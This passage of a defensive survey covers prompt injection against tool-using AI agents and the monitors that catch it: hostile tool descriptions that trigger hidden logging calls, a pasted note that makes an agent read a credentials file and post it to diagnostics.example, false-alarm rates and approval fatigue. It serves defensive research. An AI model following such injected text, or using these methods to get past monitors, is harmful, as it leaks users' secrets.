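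The method also depends on the agent's written reasoning. When the researchers linked calls only by their order in time, the share of entry points found fell from 91 to 74 per cent on another 100 attacks. When a language model compared the calls directly with the user's wording, without the structured list of permitted steps, the share fell to 64 per cent.

### Hostile text in a tool description

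IPIGuard's planner trusts the tool descriptions as well as the request. Hu, Fan and colleagues (2026), in *Log-To-Leak*, studied attackers who run a tool server that the user has connected. Text in one of the server's tool descriptions leads the agent to make an additional logging call after it has finished the user's task. That call sends the attacker the user's question and the data that another server returned. The researchers tested three defences on GPT-4o with GitHub's tools:

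| Defence | Sessions with the extra logging call (per cent) |
|---|---|
| None | 62.64 |
| Repeating the user's request | 59.58 |
| IPIGuard | 60.47 |
| A language model that screens tool descriptions | 55.38 |

IPIGuard made almost no difference. Hu and colleagues don't explain why, but the planner probably read the hostile description and included the logging call in its plan. IPIGuard would then have treated the call as approved.

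Two detectors that look for injected text also did badly. DataSentinel flagged none of the 100 hostile descriptions. The other detector flagged 91 of them, but also 136 of 159 harmless ones. Tool descriptions normally contain instructions about when and how to call the tool, so finding instructions in a description is weak evidence that it is hostile.

Hu and colleagues conclude that a tool's description shouldn't be able to authorise a disclosure. They suggest that the software running the agent should check data passing from one server to another, or ask the user before an extra logging call, but they haven't tested either measure. A source-to-sink rule could also flag the call if the operator labels the attacker's server as an outside destination and the first server's data as private.

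### Hostile text in the user's message

Trace B is harder still, because the hostile text is part of the request. The results for IPIGuard, AgentSentry and AgentTracer don't cover this case, because An and colleagues treat the user's instruction as reliable, and Yao and colleagues and Zhang and colleagues assume that the attacker can't change it. Other research on prompt injection often makes the same assumption. *SecPO* (2026), for example, which trains models to ignore injected instructions, assumes that the software indicates to the model which text to trust and that the user is well-meaning.

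If IPIGuard's planner received the developer's sentence and the pasted note together, it might write this plan:

```
1  read_file(logs/build.log)
2  read_file(config/credentials)
3  http_post(diagnostics.example, body: unknown)    needs 2
4  http_post(tracker, body: unknown)                needs 1
```

IPIGuard would then hold the agent to a plan that includes the theft. AgentSentry would probably raise no alarm, because it looks for hostile passages in tool results, and these results contain only a log and some passwords. AgentTracer might derive permission for calls 2 and 3 from the pasted note. Even if it marked them as violations, the path back from call 3 would end at the user's request instead of outside content, so it wouldn't report an injection.

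Some fixed rules fail in the same way. An operator might extend the rule about known contacts to accept any address the user supplies, since users often have a good reason to give a new one. The extended rule wouldn't flag the attacker's address, because that address is in the user's message. The source-to-sink rule still works, so an operator who adds a comparison with the request should keep that rule running and not let the request override it.

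### Treating pasted text as untrusted

The application can separate what the user typed from material they passed on. *Render Before Reading* (2026) does this by treating all attached documents, forwarded emails and meeting transcripts as untrusted, even those the user wrote, because the software generally can't verify where a document came from. Its defence turns untrusted text into an image before the model reads it, since models are less likely to follow instructions in images.

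Marking untrusted text is simpler but less dependable. *Prompt Injection Through Forensic Evidence* cites a 2024 study in which marking cut the success rate of attacks from over 50 per cent to below 2 per cent, although an attacker who knows a fixed marking scheme can imitate it. An and colleagues tested a version that put markers around tool results and told the model to ignore any instructions inside them. It reduced the success rate of their most effective attack only from 27.19 to 22.26 per cent.

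Withholding the pasted note from the planner is safer. Given only the developer's sentence, the planner should produce just the log read and the tracker post. The agent can still refer to the note when it writes the summary, treating it like tool output. The extra reads that IPIGuard allows would need their own limits, or the note could still get the agent to read the credentials.

The application has to record the boundary between the user's own words and other text when the text arrives. An attachment comes as a separate item, and a chat window can record that the user pasted something or that a link filled in the message, as in the Reprompt attack. A gateway that receives only the finished message can't reconstruct any of this. Even typed words may not be the user's own, because people sometimes retype instructions from a website.

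Users also paste text that they want the agent to follow, such as a colleague's list of steps. If the planner never receives the list, the agent can't do the job. AgentTracer has a compromise for files that could also apply to pasted text. If a user asks the agent to configure a system according to a manual, the agent may take steps from the manual, but only data from a file that the manual mentions. This limits which files the agent can take instructions from, but it wouldn't stop Trace B if the developer had written "follow the attached note", because the malicious instructions are in the note itself.

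### Confirming the task with the user

The application can also restate the task and ask the user to confirm it before the agent starts. For Trace B, the restatement might be: "Read the build log and the credentials file. Send the contents of the credentials file to diagnostics.example. Post a summary of the log to the tracker." This is better than approving one call at a time, because the user sees the read and the send together before any call runs.

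Ordinary software should generate the restatement of the plan that the user confirms, with exact file names and addresses. If the model that read the hidden paragraph writes it, the model may call the theft "running diagnostics" or leave it out. Even an exact restatement is incomplete when some arguments in the plan aren't known yet. For example, if the agent will look up the recipient later, the user can't confirm the address at the start, so the application has to ask again once it has the address.

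The user may also approve the theft. *Silent Egress* warns that users usually can't tell whether a network request described as a connectivity check is legitimate. *The Devil is in the Context* (2026), which classifies injection attacks, notes that people shown hidden content may not understand or reject it. The application could keep confirmations rare by asking only when the plan sends private data to an address the user didn't type, which would still cover Trace B.

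### Judging against the operator's purpose

An operator can state the agent's purpose in a place that users can't edit. The build agent's purpose, for example, might be to read files in the `logs` folder and post summaries to the tracker. Calls 2 and 3 violate this purpose whatever the user's message contains. The operator can enforce a purpose this precise with the path and destination allowlists described earlier, without using a model to interpret it.

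A general coding assistant has a broader purpose, such as helping developers with a project, which could include reading a configuration file and contacting a diagnostics service. A second model could judge whether each call fits that purpose, but if its input includes the user's message, the hidden paragraph can influence it too. Without the message, it will block more harmless work because it can't take into account a developer's good reason for an unusual call.

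AgentSentry has something close to a purpose check. When it revises an action after an alarm, it allows a tool call with outside effects only if the operator's policy permits the tool and if the user's request or other accepted evidence supports the call's sensitive arguments. Zhang and colleagues don't report how well the policy works by itself. This step probably wouldn't run in Trace B, because no alarm would trigger it.

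If the user is the attacker, comparing the calls with the operator's purpose is the only one of these three remedies that still applies. A hostile customer can type the request instead of pasting it, and will confirm it when asked. If this customer asks a service agent for another person's order history, the agent does what the request calls for when it looks up the record and reports the contents, so comparing its calls with the request reveals nothing wrong. The operator has to require that the agent retrieve only the logged-in customer's records. The software should take the customer's identity from the login, since a model might accept a false claim in the conversation.

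Checking each session against the agent's purpose can also miss an attack spread over several sessions. *The Devil is in the Context* describes malicious users who obtain pieces of information in separate conversations and combine them elsewhere. Each conversation may stay within the agent's purpose. To detect such an attack, the operator would have to link sessions by account and examine what each user has collected over time. An attacker with several accounts could still avoid detection.

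## From alerts to action: false alarms, timing and response

An operator needs to know what share of a detector's alerts are likely to be real before deciding how to respond to them. That share depends on how rare attacks are as well as on the detector.

### How many alerts are real

Suppose an operator's agents run 10,000 sessions a day and 10 of those sessions contain an attack. Both numbers are illustrative, since an operator rarely knows how often it comes under attack. Let $p$ be the share of sessions with an attack (here 0.001), $r$ the recall and $f$ the benign firing rate. Then

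$$\text{share of alerts that are real} = \frac{r\,p}{r\,p + f\,(1-p)}$$

The table applies this to the five general rules of Kekatos and colleagues, to Zavrak's XGBoost detector, and to an imaginary detector that is right half the time it raises an alert:

| Detector | Recall (per cent) | Benign firing rate (per cent) | True alerts a day | False alerts a day | Share of alerts that are real (per cent) |
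|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| General rules | 70.1 | 29.3 | 7 | 2,927 | 0.2 |
| XGBoost | 92.7 | 7.1 | 9 | 709 | 1.3 |
| Imaginary detector | 90 | 0.09 | 9 | 9 | 50 |

The last row calculates the false-alarm rate needed for half of the alerts to be real attacks. At 90 per cent recall the detector finds 9 attacks, so it can raise at most 9 false alarms among 9,990 harmless sessions, or 0.09 per cent.

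XGBoost looks far better on its own test data, where about 99 per cent of its alerts would be real because 86 per cent of the sessions contain an attack. If the operator in the example faced 100 attacks a day instead of 10, about 12 per cent of the alerts would be real.

A test needs thousands of harmless sessions to show a false-alarm rate as low as 0.09 per cent. If a detector flags none of $n$ harmless sessions, its true rate could still be as high as about $3/n$ (at 95 per cent confidence), so the test would need about 3,300 sessions without a false alarm. Kekatos and colleagues had 123. Zavrak had 605, but each test set contained only about a fifth of them, so one false alarm there amounts to roughly 0.8 per cent. The tests of Agent-Sentry and Tether used about 1,500 harmless sessions each, but both systems blocked roughly 5 per cent of them. Of the detectors described in earlier sections,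 none that researchers tested on recorded sessions has shown a rate near 0.09 per cent.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a larger test, on 10,000 real tool calls by the company's employees. The classifier wrongly blocked 0.4 per cent of them. The chance of at least one wrong block in a session is higher, because a session contains many calls. If the errors were independent, it would be nearly 10 per cent for a session with 25 calls.

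The classifier gets its false-alarm rate down to 0.4 per cent in two stages. A fast yes-or-no filter flags 8.5 per cent of harmless calls. The model then reasons at length about only the flagged calls and clears most of the harmless ones. This second stage also clears some attacks, which raised the share missed from 1.8 to 5.7 per cent in a test on 1,000 synthetic data thefts. An operator could combine a graph rule with a slower review in the same way, and would face the same trade-off between false alarms and missed attacks.

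### Deciding before the send

A correct alert can still come too late. Zavrak's detector reads finished sessions and is meant for audits and investigations. It would score Trace B after call 4, when the attacker already has the credentials. The team would at least learn which passwords and keys to replace.

To stop the theft, software has to decide whether to block call 3 before it runs. At that point the graph contains two finished calls and one pending call. The source-to-sink rule can work with this partial graph because the arguments of call 3 already exist and the rule uses nothing that comes later. A detector trained on whole sessions would have less text to judge than it had in training. Zavrak considers live detection a natural extension but says it needs a policy for acting on partial evidence.

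The software could also act after call 2, as soon as the agent has read the credentials. That leaves more time to respond but produces more false alarms, because every session that reads the file for a good reason looks the same as an attack at that point.

Kekatos and colleagues measured how early their general rules fired on the 1,931 successful attacks in their AgentDojo recordings. The rules fired before the final harmful call in 52.4 per cent of attacks, only at that call in 17.7 per cent, and never in 29.9 per cent. When they fired early, the median lead was one tool call. A gateway that holds each call until the rules have checked it could therefore have acted in time in up to 70.1 per cent of the attacks, compared with at most 52.4 per cent for a monitor that checks each call only after it has run.

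Some of the early alerts may have been lucky, because the rules also flag payments and messages that the user wanted. An alert about a harmless email helps against a later theft only if the operator pauses the whole session. On STAC, where each chain builds up to one harmful last step, the rules fired before that step in only 11.8 per cent of cases and on the step itself in 61.5 per cent.

### Responses to an alert in Trace B

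Suppose the source-to-sink rule raises an alert while call 3 is pending. The operator has several possible responses, listed here from the cheapest to the most expensive:

| Response | Effect in Trace B | Cost if the alarm is false |
|---|---|---|
| Hold call 3 and show the developer the whole path | The credentials stay put unless the developer approves | A short wait |
| Block `diagnostics.example` | No agent can send anything there | A useful service is unavailable until someone lifts the block |
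| Withdraw `http_post` for the session | The agent can't try another address, but can't post the summary either | The developer posts the summary by hand |
| End the session | The hidden paragraph and the credentials leave the model's context | The developer loses unfinished work |
| Replace the credentials | Stolen copies stop working | Every service that uses them needs new ones |

Holding the call is easy to undo, because the operator can simply release it. The developer needs more than the pending call to judge it, though. A useful request for approval might look like this:

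```
You asked for   a summary of logs/build.log on the tracker
Now waiting     http_post to diagnostics.example
It would send   data from config/credentials, read in call 2
```

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested a display of this kind. In their main example, a user allows an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. A hidden instruction leads the agent to copy the raw invoices into a file, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name is ordinary, so the request looks fine without the history. Eighty volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe, using one of four displays:

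| Display | Unsafe requests approved (per cent) | Legitimate requests approved (per cent) | Median time (seconds) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0 | 91.7 | 16.3 |
| Exact arguments of the call | 43.3 | 90.0 | 23.4 |
| Arguments, the user's original instruction and a full log | 32.5 | 87.5 | 38.6 |
| The same facts, with the combined effect in one statement | 24.2 | 85.8 | 33.2 |

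Most of the improvement came from showing people the facts. Combining the facts into one statement seems to help further, but the evidence is weak, with only 20 people per display. After adjustment, the difference between the last two displays could plausibly range from 20 percentage points fewer unsafe approvals to 4 points more. For violations that depended on a link across several steps, people approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests with either display. Even with the best display, people approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests, so an operator shouldn't let a single click release a secret to an unknown address.

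The software behind the display can also block calls by itself. It records which files came from which, and compares each pending action with the restrictions that the user stated. With blocking switched on, a small Llama model carried out an unauthorised action in 6 of 120 runs, down from 52, and completed 100 harmless tasks, down from 104. In a separate test on prepared cases, the software detected 86.2 per cent of violations that depended on earlier steps. It detected 60.0 per cent without the links between files, and 20.0 per cent without any memory of earlier steps. This is some of the clearest evidence that the links help to detect such violations, although the cases came from only 16 attack templates, which the researchers wrote themselves.

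Blocking the destination protects other developers who paste the same note, but the attacker may have a second address. The credentials also remain in the model's context, and any later call could include them. Withdrawing `http_post` prevents the agent from sending them with that tool. The developer loses the automatic post in call 4 but can still read the summary in the chat.

Anthropic takes a milder approach in auto mode. The software returns the refusal to the agent as a tool result, with an instruction to look for a safer way to do the task. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, it stops the agent and prompts the user. If no user is present, it ends the process. In Trace B, the agent could move on to the tracker post after call 3 is refused. The hidden paragraph would still be in its context, so the software would have to keep checking every send.

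Ending the session removes the paragraph and the credentials from the context, but it can't recall anything the agent has already sent. If call 3 has run, the team has to replace the credentials and check whether anyone has used the old ones. The team may want to do this even if the software stopped the call, because any outside company that hosts the model has already received the credentials. The team has no equivalent step for a stolen client list.

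The false alarm rate limits which of these responses an operator can automate. With 709 false alerts a day, holding a call each time would be a nuisance, but the team couldn't work if credentials were replaced that often.

### Approval fatigue

Holding a call for approval works only if someone reads the request. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users approve 97 per cent of permission prompts. Most of those prompts are probably for safe commands, so the figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. The company's study of 1,053 paid developers, described earlier, is stronger evidence, because they refused about 17 per cent of the dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts. They were working in a test environment, and might have taken more care with their own projects.

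Smaller studies describe the same habit. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), software practitioners report clicking through familiar prompts and skipping review under time pressure. In *Options, Not Clicks* (2026), only three of 16 AI agent users said they read prompts carefully, and 13 said they chose "Always Allow" just to get rid of them.

The approval prompts are partly at fault. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files and found that user review played a part in 105. In 80 of these, the user had approved actions automatically. In 31, the prompt showed a command without its effect on the files.

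Asking users for approval less often doesn't solve the problem by itself. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people without a software background supervise an agent through a simulated day. The agent attempted 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group set rules in advance to allow, forbid or ask about broad kinds of action, such as spending money. These rules cut the average number of prompts from 18.0 to 10.9, but the share of excessive actions this group blocked was about 20 percentage points lower than among people who reviewed each action.

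The participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed most decisions. They approved 133 of the 148 excessive actions that went ahead. The agent in this study overstepped without an attacker, but a person who approves a payment they didn't request may well also approve one caused by prompt injection.

People seem to pay more attention to plans than to individual permission requests. Anthropic reports that users reject 39 per cent of the plans Claude Code presents, compared with 3 per cent of the requests. They may reject a plan because they prefer a different solution, so the gap doesn't measure how well they detect attacks. But it suggests that they read plans, which supports asking for approval rarely and showing the file read and the send together.

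Reviewing alerts also takes time. In the study by Hossain and colleagues, people took 33 seconds per alert with the best display. At that rate, reviewing the XGBoost detector's 718 daily alerts would take more than six and a half hours.

### Delay and computing cost

Fixed rules take very little computing power to run. Kekatos and colleagues measured MonPoly at 52,000 to about 800,000 events a second, using 8 to 14 megabytes of memory. If each of the 10,000 sessions in the example produced 50 events, MonPoly would process the whole day's log in about ten seconds at the slowest of these speeds. The gate by Hossain and colleagues took a median of 24 milliseconds per check and made no extra calls to a language model.

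Learned detectors take more computing time. Zavrak's detector spends most of it converting text into numbers, though an operator can store the results for calls that recur. Anthropic saves money by not sending file reads, or edits inside the project folder, to its classifier. In Trace B, call 2 would therefore run without a check, and call 3 would be the first chance to stop the theft. Defences that rerun the agent's steps are slower still. AgentSentry, for example, more than doubled the average time for a harmless task.

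Incomplete logs can also stop an agent from finishing harmless tasks. The gate by Hossain and colleagues blocks any action it lacks the records to judge. When the researchers removed some of the records, the share of harmless tasks completed fell from 83.3 to 76.7 per cent. An operator could send such cases to a person instead, but that person would have more prompts to answer.

### Monitors in daily use

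OpenAI has a language model review the sessions of its employees' coding agents. SecurityBrief New Zealand reports that over five months this monitor covered tens of millions of sessions and raised about 1,000 alerts of moderate severity, and that OpenAI staff caused many of them by testing the system. Assuming at least 10 million sessions, that is at most about one alert per 10,000.

This is well below the 0.09 per cent in the example, so a monitor can run at scale without flooding its reviewers. But the monitor looks for agents that act against their instructions in general, not specifically for prompt injection. It flagged every case that employees had reported, but its recall is unclear because it may have missed attacks that nobody noticed. According to AI News, the monitor finishes its review within 30 minutes of the end of a session, and OpenAI hopes eventually to block actions before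 they run. In July 2026 OpenAI described another monitor, for long-running agents, which reads the whole session so far and can pause it and alert the user.

Anthropic uses auto mode for all its internal work with Claude Code. In one case, after an upload to an internal drive failed, the agent tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site, and the classifier blocked it. This was a source followed by a sink, but no attacker was involved. In the company's two other published examples, agents also overstepped without an attacker.

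At Gusto, a customer, about 10 per cent of sessions since mid-May have had at least one refusal. Anthropic takes this as a sign that the classifier is useful and doesn't slow legitimate tasks, but the figure measures only how often it intervenes. Without knowing how many refusals were justified, one can't calculate recall or a false alarm rate from it.

Anthropic also compared manual approval with auto mode in real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for occurred in 6.3 per cent of the manual-approval sessions and 2.4 per cent of the auto-mode sessions. A model graded the sessions. Users had also chosen their own mode, so people with riskier projects may have preferred manual approval.

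Auto mode has a weakness in Trace B. To protect the classifier from injected text, Anthropic withholds tool results from it and shows it only the user's messages and the agent's calls. The pasted note is part of a user message, so the hidden paragraph would reach the classifier looking like the developer's consent. Anthropic has since added a rule that may help, which is that the classifier should never approve sending code or secrets outside, even at the user's request.

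### Attackers who adapt

The recall figures mostly come from fixed collections of attacks, written without knowledge of the detector being tested. A real attacker can observe what gets through and try again. If a detector had a 92.7 per cent chance of catching each attempt, independently of the others, an attacker with ten attempts would have a 53 per cent chance of getting at least one past it. But the failed attempts would raise alerts, giving the operator a chance to respond before one succeeds.

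In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) designed attacks for each of 12 published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks (attempts by users to make a model break its own rules). Some attacks were automated searches that used the outcome of each attempt to improve the next. Others came from a competition with more than 500 participants. The attacks succeeded more than 90 per cent of the time against most of the defences, although the original papers had reported rates near zero for the majority. Two defences that rely on special prompts let through as little as 1 per cent of AgentDojo's standard attacks, but more than 95 per cent of the attacks designed for them.

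The results from Nasr and colleagues show that a low attack success rate on a fixed set of attacks is weak evidence that a defence will stop an attacker who studies it. Such a test is better evidence of failure than of safety, because a detector that misses old attacks will probably miss new ones too. However, the attackers in the study had a lot of computing power and many attempts, which few real attackers would have against a particular company. The results also don't show that a rule about data flow would fail as badly as a defensive prompt.

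In tests, monitors for tool calls also detected less when attacks were adapted to them, though the losses were smaller. When Hossain and colleagues adapted attacks to their monitor, its recall on violations that depend on earlier steps fell from 86.2 to 75.0 per cent. They prepared these attacks in advance, and an attacker who kept adjusting might evade the monitor more often.

The safety organisation Apollo Research tested a classifier for Anthropic by inserting synthetic attacks into real coding sessions. After Anthropic strengthened the classifier, the share of attacks it missed fell from 12 to 7 per cent. It also caught about half of the attacks it had previously missed in a separate set that Anthropic never received, so the improvement extended beyond the known examples.

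Some controls still work when an attack is worded in a new way because they don't have to recognise it. A destination allowlist blocks `diagnostics.example` however persuasive the note is. A sponsored article in SC Media, by an author at the security company Sophos, recommends several more, including keeping credentials out of the agent's reach. A separate program holds the key and adds it to a request when needed, so the agent has no key to reveal.

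If the agent can choose the address, an injected instruction could still direct that program to send the key to the attacker's server. The article therefore recommends tools with a fixed destination. For the build team, that would mean limiting `http_post` to the tracker. An attacker's note could still get the agent to put private data into the summary, so the team would also have to check who can read the tracker.
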